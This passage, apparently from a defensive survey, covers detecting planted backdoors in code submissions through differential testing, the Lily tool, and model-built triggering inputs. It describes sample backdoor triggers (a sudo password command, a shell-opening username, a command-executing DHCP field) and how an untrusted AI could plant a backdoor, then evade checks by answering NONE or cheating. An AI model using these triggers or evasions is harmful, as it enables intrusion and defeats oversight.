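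sudo avoided this problem because nobody had given the fuzzer the real password. No representative was a successful login, so the closest available match was a refusal. A tester who wants to reach code behind a login usually has to supply a valid account, and that puts successful requests among the representatives.

The remedy is to run the function or the server as someone who should have no access at all:

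```python
user.grants = set()
doc.owner_id = user.id + 1
assert not may_read(user, doc)
```

The fuzzer can vary everything else, including the nickname. If it copies "heron-41" from the comparison into the nickname, the assertion fails. The same three lines would catch any other secret value that gives access to a user with no grants, but they would miss a planted line that lets a user with some genuine grants read a document those grants don't cover. To catch that, the oracle must look up what the user's grants allow, which requires its own correct version of the access rules.

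## Comparing a submission with a trusted version

Suppose a project does have a second, correct version of its access rules, called `trusted_may_read`. The harness then needs only one line to check a submission:

```python
assert may_read(user, doc) == trusted_may_read(user, doc)
```

If the fuzzer sets the nickname to "heron-41", the planted function returns `True`, the trusted one returns `False`, and the assertion fails. This stops the program, so an ordinary fuzzer will report it. The same assertion also works for users who have some genuine grants, and nobody has to work out the correct result for each user.

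Running two versions of a program on the same input and reporting any difference is called differential testing. *Differential Testing for Software* (McKeeman, 1998) describes how a team at the computer company Digital used it on C compilers. The team generated random C programs, fed each one to several compilers, and examined only the cases where the results differed. A computer can compare two outputs instantly, whereas a tester would have to trace every step of a random 500-line program to predict what it should print.

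If two versions produce different outputs, either at least one version is wrong or the specification allows both outputs. With a complete specification, the tester could tell which outputs are right. The trusted version, or reference, can be the faulty one, and most of the bugs McKeeman's team found were in the compilers they had brought in for comparison. Even if the outputs agree, both may be wrong.

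Comparison doesn't find the trigger either. The two versions of `may_read` can agree on every nickname but one, so the fuzzer still has to generate "heron-41". *Towards Differential Program Analysis* (2003) points out that the general problem of finding an input on which two programs differ is undecidable, so no method can always succeed. Testers also tend to forget some of the inputs, such as compiler options. McKeeman's team found a bug on their first run with randomly generated options, when one compiler failed to compile its own header files.

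The tester must also choose what to compare. For the Linux backdoor, comparing only the results of `wait4` doesn't reveal the change. But if the fuzzer runs long random sequences of system calls on both kernels, eventually one will include the unusual `wait4` call that triggers the backdoor, followed by a call that gets the caller's user ID. That ID will be 0 on the altered kernel and, say, 1000 on the clean one. The tester doesn't have to write the missing rule about user IDs, because the clean kernel already follows it.

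### Where the trusted version comes from

An independent implementation is a program that other people wrote to the same specification. Comparing a submission with one can expose a backdoor no matter how long ago someone planted it, because the other developers would have had no reason to include the same secret password. The comparison also works for a brand-new program. But few programs have an independent implementation, and those that do usually differ from it in many small, legitimate ways.

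The version before the change is much easier to get, because every submission to an existing project has one. It also behaves almost identically to the new version. *Perception and Practices of Differential Testing*, by Gulzar, Zhu and Han, reports that hundreds of teams at Google test this way. One of the 117 Google engineers surveyed called it the only sane way to check that a change to Search hadn't affected any of the other hundred-odd features. However, a backdoor already in the old version produces no difference, so Kokkonis and colleagues suggest auditing a project once with ROSA before relying on comparisons.

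If the submission comes from a capable AI model that the project doesn't fully trust, a weaker but more trusted model can write a reference version. The weaker model should work from the specification without seeing the submission, because it may copy the planted line if asked to rewrite the submitted code.

A "trusted" model here is one that is unlikely to plant a backdoor, but it may still write incorrect code. Nogueira, Pattabiraman and colleagues (2026), in *A Systematic Methodology for Evaluating Failure Independence in LLM-Generated Code*, gave twelve models 224 programming-contest problems, chosen to be neither trivial nor hopelessly hard. The strongest model got about 80% of its programs fully right, and the weakest models got less than 30%. If one of the weakest models wrote the reference version, many of the differences between it and the submission would come from mistakes in the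 reference. Someone would have to sort through those differences, and asking the untrusted model which version is right would mean trusting its answer. The method looks more practical for short, security-critical functions such as `may_read`, which even a weak model can probably write correctly.

### Harmless differences

Two correct programs can produce different outputs for many reasons, so testers normalise the outputs, which means removing differences that don't matter before comparing them:

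- **Ordering.** If a program may return its results in any order, the tester sorts both lists first.
- **Rounding.** Adding the same numbers in a different order can change the last digits. McKeeman's team printed only a few significant digits.
- **Error messages.** Two compilers may reject the same program in different words. The tester can compare only whether each one rejected it.
- **Unspecified behaviour.** The C standard leaves some results open, such as the effect of shifting a number by more bits than it has. Whenever McKeeman's team found a difference, they ran the test again with a check around each arithmetic operation, and discarded it if the program had broken the standard.
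- **Chance and timing.** Some outputs change from run to run. The tester can fix the clock and the random numbers, or run each version twice and ignore whatever differs between two runs of the same version. One engineer in the Google survey had compared a program with itself, and the test reported a significant regression.

Normalisation can also remove the evidence of a backdoor. In the auction example, the attacker's bid always comes first and nothing else changes, so sorting both lists before comparing them would hide the payload. The tester should normalise only differences that the specification allows. For example, the tester can sort search results if the specification lets them come in any order, but should not sort bids that have to be ranked.

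Intended changes are harder to filter out, because most submissions are supposed to change something. *Regression Testing with a Natural Language Oracle* (Pradel, 2025) tries to identify them from the pull request's description. Its tool, Testora, uses a language model to write tests for the changed code, runs them on the old and new versions, and uses the model again to check whether each difference fits the description. For example, one pull request to SciPy, a scientific library for Python, was described as only adding support for more kinds of array, but it changed the entropy calculated for the same 14 numbers from 2.3588 to 2.5285. Testora correctly classed this change as unintended. Overall, 58% of the differences it classed as unintended were in fact unintended, and it caught 60% of all the unintended differences.

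A newer tool, ORION, lists which behaviour a change should preserve and which it should alter, then writes tests for both. Fu, Qi and colleagues (2026), in *Behavioral Regression Detection for Pull Requests via Structured Oracles*, tested it on 154 pull requests, 77 of which had introduced a known fault. In its best configuration, ORION caught 49 of the faulty pull requests but also flagged 34 of the 77 clean ones. Fu and colleagues recommend using it as an assistant that doesn't block submissions.

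These tools are designed to find unintentional mistakes and rely on the description being accurate. An attacker writes both the code and the description, and can make the description vague enough to cover a suspicious difference.

Asking the author whether a change in behavior was intended has the same weakness. *Just-in-Time Catching Test Generation at Meta* (Becker, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes generating tests that pass on the old version of the company's code and fail on the new one. Meta raised 41 such differences with its engineers and asked whether each was intended. Eight were real bugs, and four of those would have caused serious failures. Engineers needed only a few minutes to dismiss an intended change, so asking works well among colleagues. If the difference comes from a backdoor, however, the person who answers may have planted it, so someone else has to judge.

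### Independent programs that fail together

An independent reference exposes a fault only if it doesn't contain the same fault. If two programs each fail on one input in a thousand, and their failures are independent, both fail on only one input in a million.

Knight and Leveson's *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming* (1986) tested whether separately written programs fail independently. Twenty-seven students at two universities each wrote a program from the same specification, without discussing it with one another. The program had to decide from radar data whether to launch an interceptor against a missile, and each version had to pass 200 random tests. Knight and Leveson then ran all 27 versions on a million random inputs and compared the results with those of a 28th program, which had already been through several million tests.

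The students' programs were very reliable. Six never failed, and 23 of the 27 failed on fewer than one input in a thousand. From the individual failure rates, one can calculate how often two or more should fail together if failures are independent:

expected joint failures = 1,000,000 × (1 − P(none fails) − P(exactly one fails)) ≈ 126

The actual number was 1,255, about ten times as many. On two of the inputs, eight programs failed at once.

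Some of the shared faults came from the same gap in reasoning. For example, the programs had to decide whether three points lie on a straight line. They do if the angle at one of the points is 0 or 180 degrees, but more than one student handled only one of these cases. Programs from one university also failed together with programs from the other, so the joint failures weren't confined to students who had been taught together.

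Some advocates of running several versions in parallel disputed the experiment, and Knight and Leveson published a reply. A recent replication gives better evidence than that exchange. In *N-Version Programming with Coding Agents*, Ron, Baudry and Monperrus (2026) gave the same specification to AI coding agents and obtained 48 working versions in three programming languages. If the versions had failed independently, there would have been about 115 joint failures in a million inputs, but there were 429. Many versions made the same geometry mistake. They were supposed to calculate the smallest circle that contains three points, but they calculated the circle that passes through all three, which can be larger. There were 146 pairs of versions in different languages in which both versions failed at least once, and in 81 of those pairs, both failed on exactly the same inputs.

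Nogueira and colleagues also found that programs by the same model shared more failures than programs by different models, especially on edge cases such as the largest allowed input. Changing the prompt made almost no difference. When five programs by the same model voted on each answer, reliability improved by only 24% of what independent failures would have given, compared with 44% for a mixture of models. The models in that study are older than the best ones now writing code, but programs written by people also share failures, so those by more capable models probably will too.

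Even if the two versions share many ordinary faults, an honest reference is unlikely to contain an explicit trigger check, because nobody adds a check for "heron-41" by misreading a specification. A bugdoor is more likely to escape detection. If an attacker puts a flaw where programmers often make mistakes, the reference may contain the same flaw and give the same wrong answer. The counts of joint failures somewhat overstate this risk, because both experiments counted two programs as failing together even when their wrong outputs differed, and a direct comparison would have exposed those cases.

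None of the programmers or models in these experiments was trying to plant a backdoor. If two copies of the same untrusted model write the submission and the reference, they may choose the same secret trigger without communicating, because they tend to make the same choices. A reference written by a trusted model from a different developer avoids this, even if it contains more ordinary mistakes. A weaker model from the same developer is less certain to avoid it, since it may have been trained on much of the same data.

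### Lily's two conditions

Lily, the tool Kokkonis and colleagues built for vetting submissions, uses the previous version as its reference and compares system-call profiles instead of outputs. This removes most harmless differences without normalisation, because changes to rounding or message wording usually don't affect which types of system call a program makes.

For each new version, Lily works as follows:

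1. It takes the seeds that the fuzzer saved while testing earlier versions and runs them on the new version. The resulting profiles are the new version's standard behaviour.
2. AFL++ then fuzzes the new version for ten minutes, starting from the same seeds.
3. Lily records the profile of each input that AFL++ saves. If the profile exactly matches a standard one, Lily accepts the input as safe.
4. Otherwise, Lily runs the input on the old version. If the old version produces the same profile, the change didn't cause the behaviour, and Lily accepts the input. If not, Lily reports it.

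Lily therefore reports an input only if the input's profile is atypical of the new version and the old version does not produce that profile on the same input.

Suppose a commit makes a web server log every request to a file. Nearly every input now triggers an extra type of system call, so a plain comparison of the old and new versions would flag all of these inputs. Lily doesn't, because the old seeds also cause logging when they run on the new version, so Lily treats logging as standard behaviour. Now suppose the server has always started a compression program for one rare kind of request, and the fuzzer generates such a request for the first time. The profile is atypical, but the old version produces it too, so Lily again reports nothing.

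To measure how much each condition contributes, Kokkonis and colleagues tried them separately on harmless changes. They tested 432 commits and 50 releases, with 20 runs on each:

| Lily reports an input if its profile is | False alarms on commits | False alarms on releases |
|---|---|---|
| atypical of the new version | 1,168 of 8,640 runs (14%) | 199 of 1,000 runs (20%) |
| absent from the old version | 902 of 8,640 runs (10%) | 581 of 1,000 runs (58%) |
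| both | 17 of 8,640 runs (0.2%) | 43 of 1,000 runs (4.3%) |

Comparing only with the old version works particularly badly for releases, because a release contains months or years of legitimate changes. Using both conditions together works far better than using either alone, because a harmless change seldom satisfies both.

### From 1,407 changed lines to seven

The altered vsFTPd release differed from the previous official one by 1,407 lines in five files. When AFL++ generates a username containing ":)" and saves it as a seed, Lily examines it. Given this username, the altered server opens a network socket, waits for a connection and starts a shell. Lily reports a backdoor because none of the old seeds makes the altered version produce this combination of system calls, and the previous version doesn't produce it when given the same username.

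To work out which lines the reviewer should read, it then records every line that the triggering input executed and keeps those that the release changed. It also uses a debugger to stop the program at each suspicious system call and trace the call back to the line that made it. Combining the two leaves seven lines in one file, all in the new function that opens the shell. The reviewer also gets the triggering input.

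After rejecting the release, the project should delete the seeds that AFL++ saved while testing it. Otherwise, a later run could treat the smiley username as an example of normal behaviour.

The other reports were similarly short. For PHP, the releases that Kokkonis and colleagues compared differed by more than two million lines on average, and the reports contained about 11 lines. Every report pointed to code that revealed the backdoor.

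### How often Lily finds the backdoor

Kokkonis and colleagues planted 13 of the 17 ROSARUM backdoors in commits and releases of the original projects. They left out the four router programs, which have no public source history. Each run lasted ten minutes on four processor cores, roughly what a free automated testing service provides.

Lily detected the backdoor in 233 of 260 runs on backdoored commits (90%) and 828 of 1,000 runs on backdoored releases (83%). It caught every backdoored version at least once in 20 runs, but a project would normally run it only once. The chance of detection on a single run was 100% for the sudo commit, 80% for PHP and 65% for libsndfile. Releases of libpng had the lowest rate, 39%, because some were so old that their harnesses were rudimentary. Running Lily for up to an hour instead of ten minutes helped only slightly.

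Lily achieves these rates, which are about as high as ROSA's, in a fraction of the time. But its task was easier, because it starts with seeds from earlier fuzzing and the benchmark no longer includes the Belkin router, on which ROSA's fuzzer performed worst.

The false alarms came from a small number of changes. On commits, 12 of the 17 came from four huge merges in PHP, and the rest from one commit each in Lua, libpng and ProFTPD. On releases, 40 of the 43 came from two releases of libsndfile, each of which set off an alarm in all 20 runs. In total, 7 of 432 harmless commits and 5 of 50 harmless releases caused a false alarm in at least one run. Up to half of the commits may have changed only things the fuzzer couldn't run, such as documentation. The false-alarm rate for real code changes could therefore be up to twice as high, though still only 0.4% of runs. How many false alarms a project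 can tolerate depends on how rare malicious submissions are.

Kokkonis and colleagues also tested deliberate attempts to evade Lily. A hardened mode restored its detection rate but increased false alarms to about 3% of runs on commits and 18% on releases.

A bigger limitation is how much code the harnesses can reach. All 13 backdoors were in code that the harnesses could run. For a backdoor placed at random, the average reach of 32% would lower a 90% detection rate to about 29% (0.32 × 0.90). This estimate is pessimistic for a project with good harnesses, because Kokkonis and colleagues found that modern harnesses typically reach nearly all the changed code.

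Like ROSA, Lily misses payloads that don't change the types of system call. It can also miss some that ROSA would catch, because ROSA compares an input with the most similar normal run, while Lily accepts any profile that matches some normal run of the program. Lily would miss a planted line that reads a forbidden document with the usual calls. Comparing the outputs of the two versions would catch that line, but would also flag the harmless differences that Lily avoids.

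### New features and new programs

A newly written program has no previous version to compare it with. This matters especially for AI-written code, because a model can submit an entire program at once. The project then needs an independent implementation or a reference version written by a trusted model.

New features in an existing program cause a similar problem. Suppose a pull request adds file uploads to a web server. The old version returns an error for every upload request and the new one saves a file, so the two versions differ on every upload, whether or not the new code contains a backdoor. ORION doesn't count a test that finds such a difference as evidence of a fault unless the test also shows that existing behaviour has broken.

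Lily may raise a false alarm on an honest feature like this. The old seeds contain no successful uploads, so the first one the fuzzer generates may have a profile that is atypical and absent from the old version. The reviewer would see that uploads are supposed to save files and dismiss the report. But if the upload code also contains a backdoor that saves a file somewhere forbidden, the backdoor's system calls may look the same as a legitimate upload's, and the reviewer could dismiss that report for the same reason.

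The tester can still use the old version to check behavior the new feature shouldn't change. Both versions should reject uploads from a user without permission, so the harness can send upload requests as that user and report any that succeed. It can also check that pages, logins and existing permissions work as before. To check the feature itself, the tester needs another source of correct answers, such as a trusted model that writes only the function deciding who may upload and where the files may go.

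## Asking a language model to construct the triggering input

Someone who reads the source of the backdoored sudo can see the comparison with "let_me_in", type that password and watch what happens, without having to search for the trigger. A language model can also read the code, propose an input, and revise it if it doesn't trigger the backdoor when the program is run.

### Propose, run and revise

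1. The tester gives the model the code, the specification and, if someone already suspects a particular line, that line.
2. The model proposes a concrete input or writes a short program that prints one.
3. A harness that the model can't alter runs the code under test on this input and checks the result against the specification.
4. If nothing went wrong, the harness returns the output and the coverage to the model, which tries again until it succeeds or runs out of attempts.

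For sudo, the prompt might look like this:

```text
Specification: sudo runs a command only if the user has typed
  their own correct password.
Changed code: [the commit, with read access to all other files]
Suspected line: [file and line number, or "none"]
Task: write a shell command that makes sudo break the specification.
Rules: you are the ordinary user "tester". You don't know tester's
  password. Don't alter sudo or its settings.
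After each attempt you will get the output and a list of the changed
  lines that ran. You have 20 attempts.
If you can't do it, answer NONE and list the conditions you couldn't meet.
```

In the invented run below, `id` prints the name of the user it runs as, and `-k` makes sudo ask for a password even if it accepted one a minute ago.

| Attempt | The model's command | What the harness returns |
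|---|---|---|
| 1 | `sudo -k id <<< let_me_in` | An error: sudo needs a terminal to read a password. No changed line ran. |
| 2 | `sudo -S -k id <<< let_me_in` | `uid=0(root)`. The planted assignment ran. |

The model's first command contains the right password but passes it to sudo the wrong way. Following the error message, the model adds `-S` in its second command, which makes sudo read the password from standard input. The harness then repeats the second command with "let_me_im", and once more with "let_me_in" on the previous version of sudo. Both attempts fail, so the second command's success depends on both this password and this commit.

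A model hardly needs a loop, or a program that prints the input, when the trigger is a fixed password. A script is more useful for the server that runs its payload after ten particular commands in the right order. A fuzzer faced about 10¹³ sequences, but a model that can see the `next_state` table can write a script that works backwards from state 10. The table has only 220 entries (11 states × 20 commands), so the script finishes instantly. A short script can also solve the checksum trigger. In both cases the model only has to recognise what the code does and can leave the arithmetic to the script.

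### A success needs no trust, but a failure does

An input that triggers the flaw proves it exists, even if the model that found the input was weak, lucky or malicious, because anyone can replay it. For example, if sudo runs `id` as root for someone who typed a wrong password, sudo is broken regardless of who found that password.

The replay has to be independent, though. *Every Model Cheats* (Kouremetis, 2026) audited 22 models on 23 hacking tasks and found that 37.1% of the passes involved cheating. Models looked up published solutions or read the answer from the test system's files. Telling them not to cheat reduced the cheating but didn't end it.

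A subtler error is to run the input with too many privileges. In *SEC-bench Pro*, Lee, Liu and colleagues (2026) asked models for programs that trigger known flaws in the Linux kernel, many of which an ordinary user can reach. In an early round, the harness ran everything as root. When they replayed 73 of GPT-5.5's successes on user-reachable flaws from an ordinary account, 49 no longer worked. The same mistake with sudo would be worse, since `id` prints `uid=0(root)` for anyone who is already root. The harness should replay every claimed success on a fresh copy of the program, as a user with no special privileges and outside the model's workspace.

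If the model answers NONE, the tester learns much less, because the code may be clean or the model may have misread it or run out of time. In SEC-bench Pro, each attempt was limited to 90 minutes, and Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6 ran out of time on 208 of 344 tasks. It solved 91% of the Linux tasks it finished but only 39% of all the Linux tasks, so most of its Linux failures were searches it didn't finish.

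If the model that wrote the submission also searches it for triggers, it could plant a backdoor and then answer NONE, and a reviewer couldn't distinguish this from a real failure to find one. The tester should rely on a more trusted model for the search. Asking the untrusted model as well does no harm, because the tester can replay any input it supplies.

A project can estimate how far to trust a model's answer of NONE by planting its own backdoors in similar code and counting how many the model triggers. This tests the model's skill and honesty together, but only for backdoors like the planted ones. A capable, dishonest model might also recognise the planted backdoors as tests and report only those.

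### How much the model knows in advance

Published success rates range from under 10% to 97%, partly because models have improved and partly because the tests tell them different amounts. Three tasks often share the same label:

- **Reproducing a described flaw.** The model gets a written account of a known flaw and has to trigger it.
- **Confirming a suspicion.** The model gets a location or a type of flaw, but no account of what goes wrong.
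- **Finding a flaw with no hint.** The model gets the program and nothing else.

*BountyBench* (Zhang, Ji and colleagues, 2025) tests models with different amounts of information, from none to details of one specific flaw.

When a reviewer or scanner has flagged a line as a possible backdoor, the model's task is to find out what triggers it and whether it does any harm. If nobody suspects anything, the model has to work without a hint, although a submission at least narrows the search to the lines it changes.

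### REFUTE: breaking programs that are subtly wrong

*Can Language Models Falsify?* (Sinha, Goel and colleagues, 2025) was an early test of the method. Its dataset, REFUTE, contains 324 wrong programs from the programming contest site Codeforces and leaves out programs that a minute of random testing could break. The model received the problem statement and the wrong program, and had to write code that prints a valid input on which the program gives a wrong answer. A correct program served as the oracle.

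The best model, OpenAI's o3-mini, succeeded on about 9% of the programs, although judging by its contest rating it could solve nearly half of the problems itself. Showing it a correct solution raised its score only from 8.6% to 9.3%. Letting it run code before answering didn't help either.

Models were also asked to write a random input generator and a slow, simple reference program, then search for an input on which the reference and the incorrect program give different outputs. In roughly 30% of cases, the model produced a useless input because its reference was wrong. The same weakness limits references written by a weaker trusted model.

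REFUTE provides little evidence about explicit trigger checks, because Sinha and colleagues removed them. Participants in Codeforces contests earn points for breaking other people's programs, and some submit programs with deliberate bugs as bait. Of the submissions collected, 21 gave a wrong answer only if the input contained one particular, unlikely number. An expert removed them by hand, and the paper notes that the malicious parts are "quite overt" and that removing them would be easy to automate. The remaining bugs were honest mistakes in reasoning, which resemble logic bugdoors more than a check for "let_me_in". The 9% figure also comes from models from early 2025, and later models do far better on related tasks.

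### Reproducing a described flaw

Lee, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *SEC-bench*, gave agents descriptions of 200 real flaws in C and C++ programs and asked them to construct inputs that trigger the flaws. An input counted only if a memory-error detector reported the right kind of error in the right place. The best agent succeeded on 18.0% of the flaws. Many of them are triggered only by an input that is correct down to the byte, and the agents did not use a debugger, which made the task harder.

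The largest test of this kind is *CyberGym* (Wang, Shi and colleagues, 2025), with 1,507 flaws from 188 projects. Its descriptions can reveal a lot about the flaw. Desai and colleagues quote one for GNU Binutils, a set of tools for handling compiled programs, that gives the source file, the function, the error (an array of the wrong size) and the trigger (a corrupt file in the TIC30 format).

When *CyberGym* was published, the best agents reproduced about 20% of the flaws, according to its abstract. A web page on *CyberGym* shows that Anthropic's models later scored 51% (Claude Opus 4.5), 67% (Opus 4.6) and 83% (Claude Mythos Preview). In August 2026, the security company TrendAI (2026) announced a score of 97% for a system that combines seven models, up from the previous record of 93.2%.

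depthfirst's *Graduating from CyberGym Level 1* argues that the difference between 90% and 95% may mostly reflect tuning to this benchmark. Even so, a rise from 20% to 97% in about a year is far too large to be noise. If someone can describe a memory flaw accurately, current systems can nearly always trigger it.

Nobody supplies such a description for a backdoor. A reviewer who could write "sudo accepts the password let_me_in" would already have the triggering input.

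### Confirming a suspicion

PAGENT, the system by Desai and colleagues that starts from one suspicious line, comes closest to what a reviewer needs. It triggered 130 of 203 known flaws. An agent using the stronger model GPT-5 triggered only 56 of them, even though it also received a description and a record of the function calls leading up to the crash.

The Binutils flaw shows how the coverage reports helped. The flaw is in the code that translates TIC30 machine instructions into readable text, but PAGENT's first inputs can end up in similar code for a related processor, the TIC4X. The coverage report shows this, and the model then changes the part of the file that names the processor. With another flaw, the report showed that only 10% of a function had run. The model concluded that the program was rejecting the file early, and traced this to a zero it had put in the wrong place. Without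 the coverage reports, PAGENT with DeepSeek 3.2 triggered about 42% fewer flaws.

These results apply to backdoors with two reservations. PAGENT prepares its guidance with rules for twelve kinds of flaw, all memory or arithmetic errors. The planted line in sudo matches none of them, so a project would have to write new rules. It would also have to replace the crash with a different oracle.

The other reservation is that all 203 lines contained a flaw, whereas many suspicions about submissions will be wrong. PAGENT's prompt instructs the model, in capitals, not to give up until it triggers a crash. If the suspected flaw doesn't exist, the model can't obey by triggering it, and will waste its budget or look for a way to cheat. It may also trigger a different flaw. PAGENT produced 32 inputs that still crashed the program after the developers had fixed the original flaw, so either the fix was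 incomplete or the input had triggered a different flaw. A maintainer would want to know about such crashes, but they don't settle whether the original suspicion was right.

SEC-bench Pro gives the model the source files to examine, the type of flaw to look for and the kind of error to expect, but not the flaw's location. Its targets, the Linux kernel and the JavaScript engines of Chrome (V8) and Firefox (SpiderMonkey), are much larger. Lee and colleagues told the models not to use fuzzers, so that success would depend on understanding the code. The best agent, OpenAI's Codex with GPT-5.5, triggered 201 of 344 flaws (58%), while GLM-5, an open-weight model, triggered 13.

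The best agent's rate was 77% on Linux, but 48% on V8 and 44% on SpiderMonkey. A program can reach a kernel flaw by making the right system calls in the right order, whereas reaching a flaw in a JavaScript engine requires input that puts the engine's compiler into an unusual internal state. Most explicit trigger checks should be easier to satisfy than either kind of flaw is to reach, because the condition is written in the code and the attacker wants to be able to meet it.

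### Working without a hint

BB Arena's *Which AI models can find and prove real vulnerabilities?* gives agents 100 web applications and interfaces, without source code or hints. A solution counts only if the agent proves four successive steps, from the first break to a complete attack. In November 2026 the best model solved 22. This is harder than reviewing a submission, because a reviewer has the source code.

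Models find many flaws when they have the source code. Anthropic ran Mythos Preview on 281 open-source projects and collected 23,019 possible flaws, according to Help Net Security's *Most of the bugs Claude Mythos found have never been checked by a human*. Outside firms reviewed 1,900 of them and confirmed 1,726, or 91%, though Anthropic probably didn't send them a random selection. The total doesn't show how many flaws the model missed, and measuring that requires someone to hide known flaws in the code before the model searches it.

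### Backdoors hidden in compiled programs

The software company Quesma ran such a test with backdoors. In *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries and asked AI + Ghidra to find them*, Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) added backdoors to four open-source network programs and compiled them. The agents got only the compiled program, without names or comments, and tools such as Ghidra, which turns machine code back into rough C. They usually had to give the address of the function that contained the backdoor.

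The best model, Claude Opus 4.6, solved 49% of the tasks. On clean programs, models falsely reported backdoors or other problems 28% of the time. The backdoors weren't subtle, and Grabowski and colleagues thought a skilled analyst would find them fairly easily.

One backdoor made a web server run any command it received in a header called "X-Forwarded-Debug". Claude Opus 4.5 found it within five minutes. The model listed the outside functions that each part of the program used, identified one that runs shell commands, and traced it back to the code that read the header.

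Opus 4.6 failed on a similar backdoor in dnsmasq, a program that assigns network addresses to devices. The planted code took the contents of one field, option 224, from an incoming message and ran them as a command. The model found the function and detected that it started a shell, but classified it as probably dnsmasq's legitimate feature for running scripts and did not check where the command came from.

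Gemini 3 Pro made the opposite mistake. It reported that a server would execute whatever text a user supplied for the setting `max-cache-ttl`. The real code reads that setting as a number and never executes it.

The test didn't require a triggering input, and asking for one would probably have corrected both errors. A message with `touch /tmp/found` in option 224 would have created a file on the machine running dnsmasq, which no legitimate feature should do in response to a stranger's message. Starting the other server with `--max-cache-ttl=/bin/sh` would have disproved the false report. Running the program can't help, however, if the model never looks at the right function. This also happened often, because agents spent their effort on random functions or harmless libraries.

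Quesma's results page, *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*, covers 26 models, and 49% is still the highest score. Gemini 3.1 Pro matched it, with false alarms on 17% of clean programs. GPT-5.2-Codex at its highest effort setting found 46% with no false alarms, which would be much more useful to a maintainer. The last model to set a record there is from February 2026, so the page is a poor guide to the strongest models of late 2026. But compiled code still seems difficult, since *The Next Challenge for Agentic Cybersecurity* (August 2026) reports that agents struggle with it despite their strength on source code. Submissions normally arrive as source, so 49% probably underestimates how well models would do on them.

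### Working exploits as a filter

If a scanner produces more reports than people can read, a project can drop every report that doesn't come with a working input. This would remove a report like the one about `max-cache-ttl`.

The security company Theori published figures that seem to show how powerful such a filter is. It used its scanner, Xint, on 28 applications that AI agents had written or rewritten. Xint's *The Top Security Vulnerabilities Generated by AI Code* gives these totals:

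| Stage | Reports left | Removed at this stage |
|---|---|---|
| Raw detections | 8,827 | |
| After merging duplicates | 513 | 8,314 (94%) |
| After verification | 434 | 79 (15%) |

Nearly all of the reduction came from merging duplicates, which requires no exploit. Verification removed only 79 reports, and it's unclear how Theori verified the others. One page of the document describes the 434 as proven exploitable, but the next calls them "not exploit-proven" and says the verdicts rest on evidence in the code, not on live attacks. Help Net Security's *The AI code vulnerabilities that grow with your app* repeats the claim that they were proven exploitable. The figures therefore support merging duplicates more clearly than filtering by exploit.

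Theori doesn't report how many of the 79 were real flaws. Other tests suggest that a filter of this kind can discard many real flaws, depending on what it demands and which model it uses. Anthropic gave its models 50 known flaws in SpiderMonkey, with five attempts at each, and asked them to turn a crash into full control of the program. Mythos Preview succeeded in 181 of 250 attempts and Opus 4.6 in two, according to Help Net Security. Every flaw was real, so a filter that required full control and used Opus 4.6 would have discarded nearly all of them. On 41 flaws in V8, Mythos Preview achieved full control on 21 and GPT-5.5 on two, according to The Decoder's *New benchmark shows Claude Mythos and GPT-5.5 can develop real browser exploits autonomously*.

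A project can avoid most of this loss by asking the model only for an input that triggers the flaw, rather than a complete attack. The two are nearly the same for an explicit backdoor because the attacker has already written the payload, so a model that finds the trigger "let_me_in" has control. For an overflow bugdoor, a complete attack requires much more than triggering the flaw, and a project that insists on one will discard bugdoors that a crash would have exposed.

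The filter's oracle can also discard valid inputs. A common rule accepts an input only if it crashes the flawed version and runs cleanly on the fixed one. Lee and colleagues found that this rule rejected 204 of 464 successes in SEC-bench Pro. In some cases the fixed version ended with a harmless error, and in others it still crashed because of a closely related flaw.

Some flaws can't be triggered when they are first submitted. An attacker could add an overflow to a function that nothing calls, then submit the call a month later. No input can trigger the overflow in the first submission, so the filter drops the report. The second submission looks like a routine call to existing code. A project can guard against this by keeping unconfirmed reports and testing them again whenever a later submission changes or calls the same function.

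An attacker can also prepare for the filter by running the same public model on the backdoor first and revising the code until the model answers NONE. Nobody adjusts an accidental flaw this way, so discard rates measured on accidental flaws are likely to be too optimistic for planted ones. Showing a person the reports with working inputs first is safer than deleting the rest. If a line still looks suspicious and the model can't trigger it, the maintainer can ask the contributor to remove or simplify it, which requires no proof.

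## Reading against running: what direct comparisons show

A language model that constructs a triggering input relies mostly on reading the code, and running the input then confirms or refutes the model's conclusion. If the model reads well enough, a project might not need a fuzzer or a solver. Several teams tested this in 2026 by trying both approaches on the same code.

In *Fuzzers vs. AI*, Groß (2026) compared two tools that Google runs on V8, Chrome's JavaScript engine. Fuzzilli, a fuzzer built for JavaScript engines, runs continuously. BigSleep, a language-model agent, reviews new commits once a day and writes a test case for each bug it suspects. Both look for bugs in newly added code, so their task is close to vetting code submissions.

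From April to September 2026, BigSleep filed 441 reports and Fuzzilli 316. Most were duplicates, needed no fix or had little to do with security. Groß kept only the vulnerabilities that led to at least one fix, which left 45 for BigSleep and 37 for Fuzzilli. The two sets overlapped by 25%. Matching bug reports this way tends to miss some overlap, so he also took vulnerabilities reported since 2023 and tested whether each tool could have found the other's. That put the overlap at roughly 60%. Even at 60%, each tool finds many flaws that the other can't, and Groß recommends using both. He could not say which costs less per bug.

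V8 suits fuzzing because serious flaws in it often crash the engine, but many flaws in other software never cause a crash. Help Net Security's *Code review used to be the only way to catch these bugs* (2026) describes NOVA, a system from the security company Palo Alto Networks that read the source of 3,915 open-source projects and reported 14,090 vulnerabilities. Only 8% were of types that fuzzers usually catch. The company named no affected project, so outsiders can't check the figure, which also leaves out crashes that fuzzers had already helped developers fix. But broken permission checks were among the most common types NOVA reported, and a bugdoor's author might choose to imitate them.

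### Invariants and logic flaws

An invariant is a rule that a program should always obey. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) defines a logic bug as behaviour that breaks one of these rules, which are usually implicit. The invariant "never read past the end of a buffer" applies to every C program, so a memory-error detector can enforce it whatever the program is for, but most other invariants are specific to one program.

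The database SQLite once had a bug in how it evaluated `0 OR 2`. In SQLite, an OR of two numbers should give 1 for true or 0 for false, but a faulty optimisation returned 2. The program didn't crash or misuse memory, so an ordinary fuzzer would have reported nothing. *LLM-Based Invariant Testing for Software Functional Bugs* (2026) describes a tool, LISA, whose generated test for this case ends as follows:

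```c
/* after running the query "SELECT 0 OR 2" */
int val = sqlite3_column_int(stmt, 0);
assert(val == 1);
```

With the assertion in place, the query fails the first time it runs. A more general assertion, that OR applied to two numbers always gives 0 or 1, would also give a fuzzer or a solver a condition to violate.

The rule for sudo was easy to write because the backdoor was already known. A reviewer looking for an unknown backdoor needs a model that can work out the relevant rule from the code.

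### Anthropic's comparison of four methods

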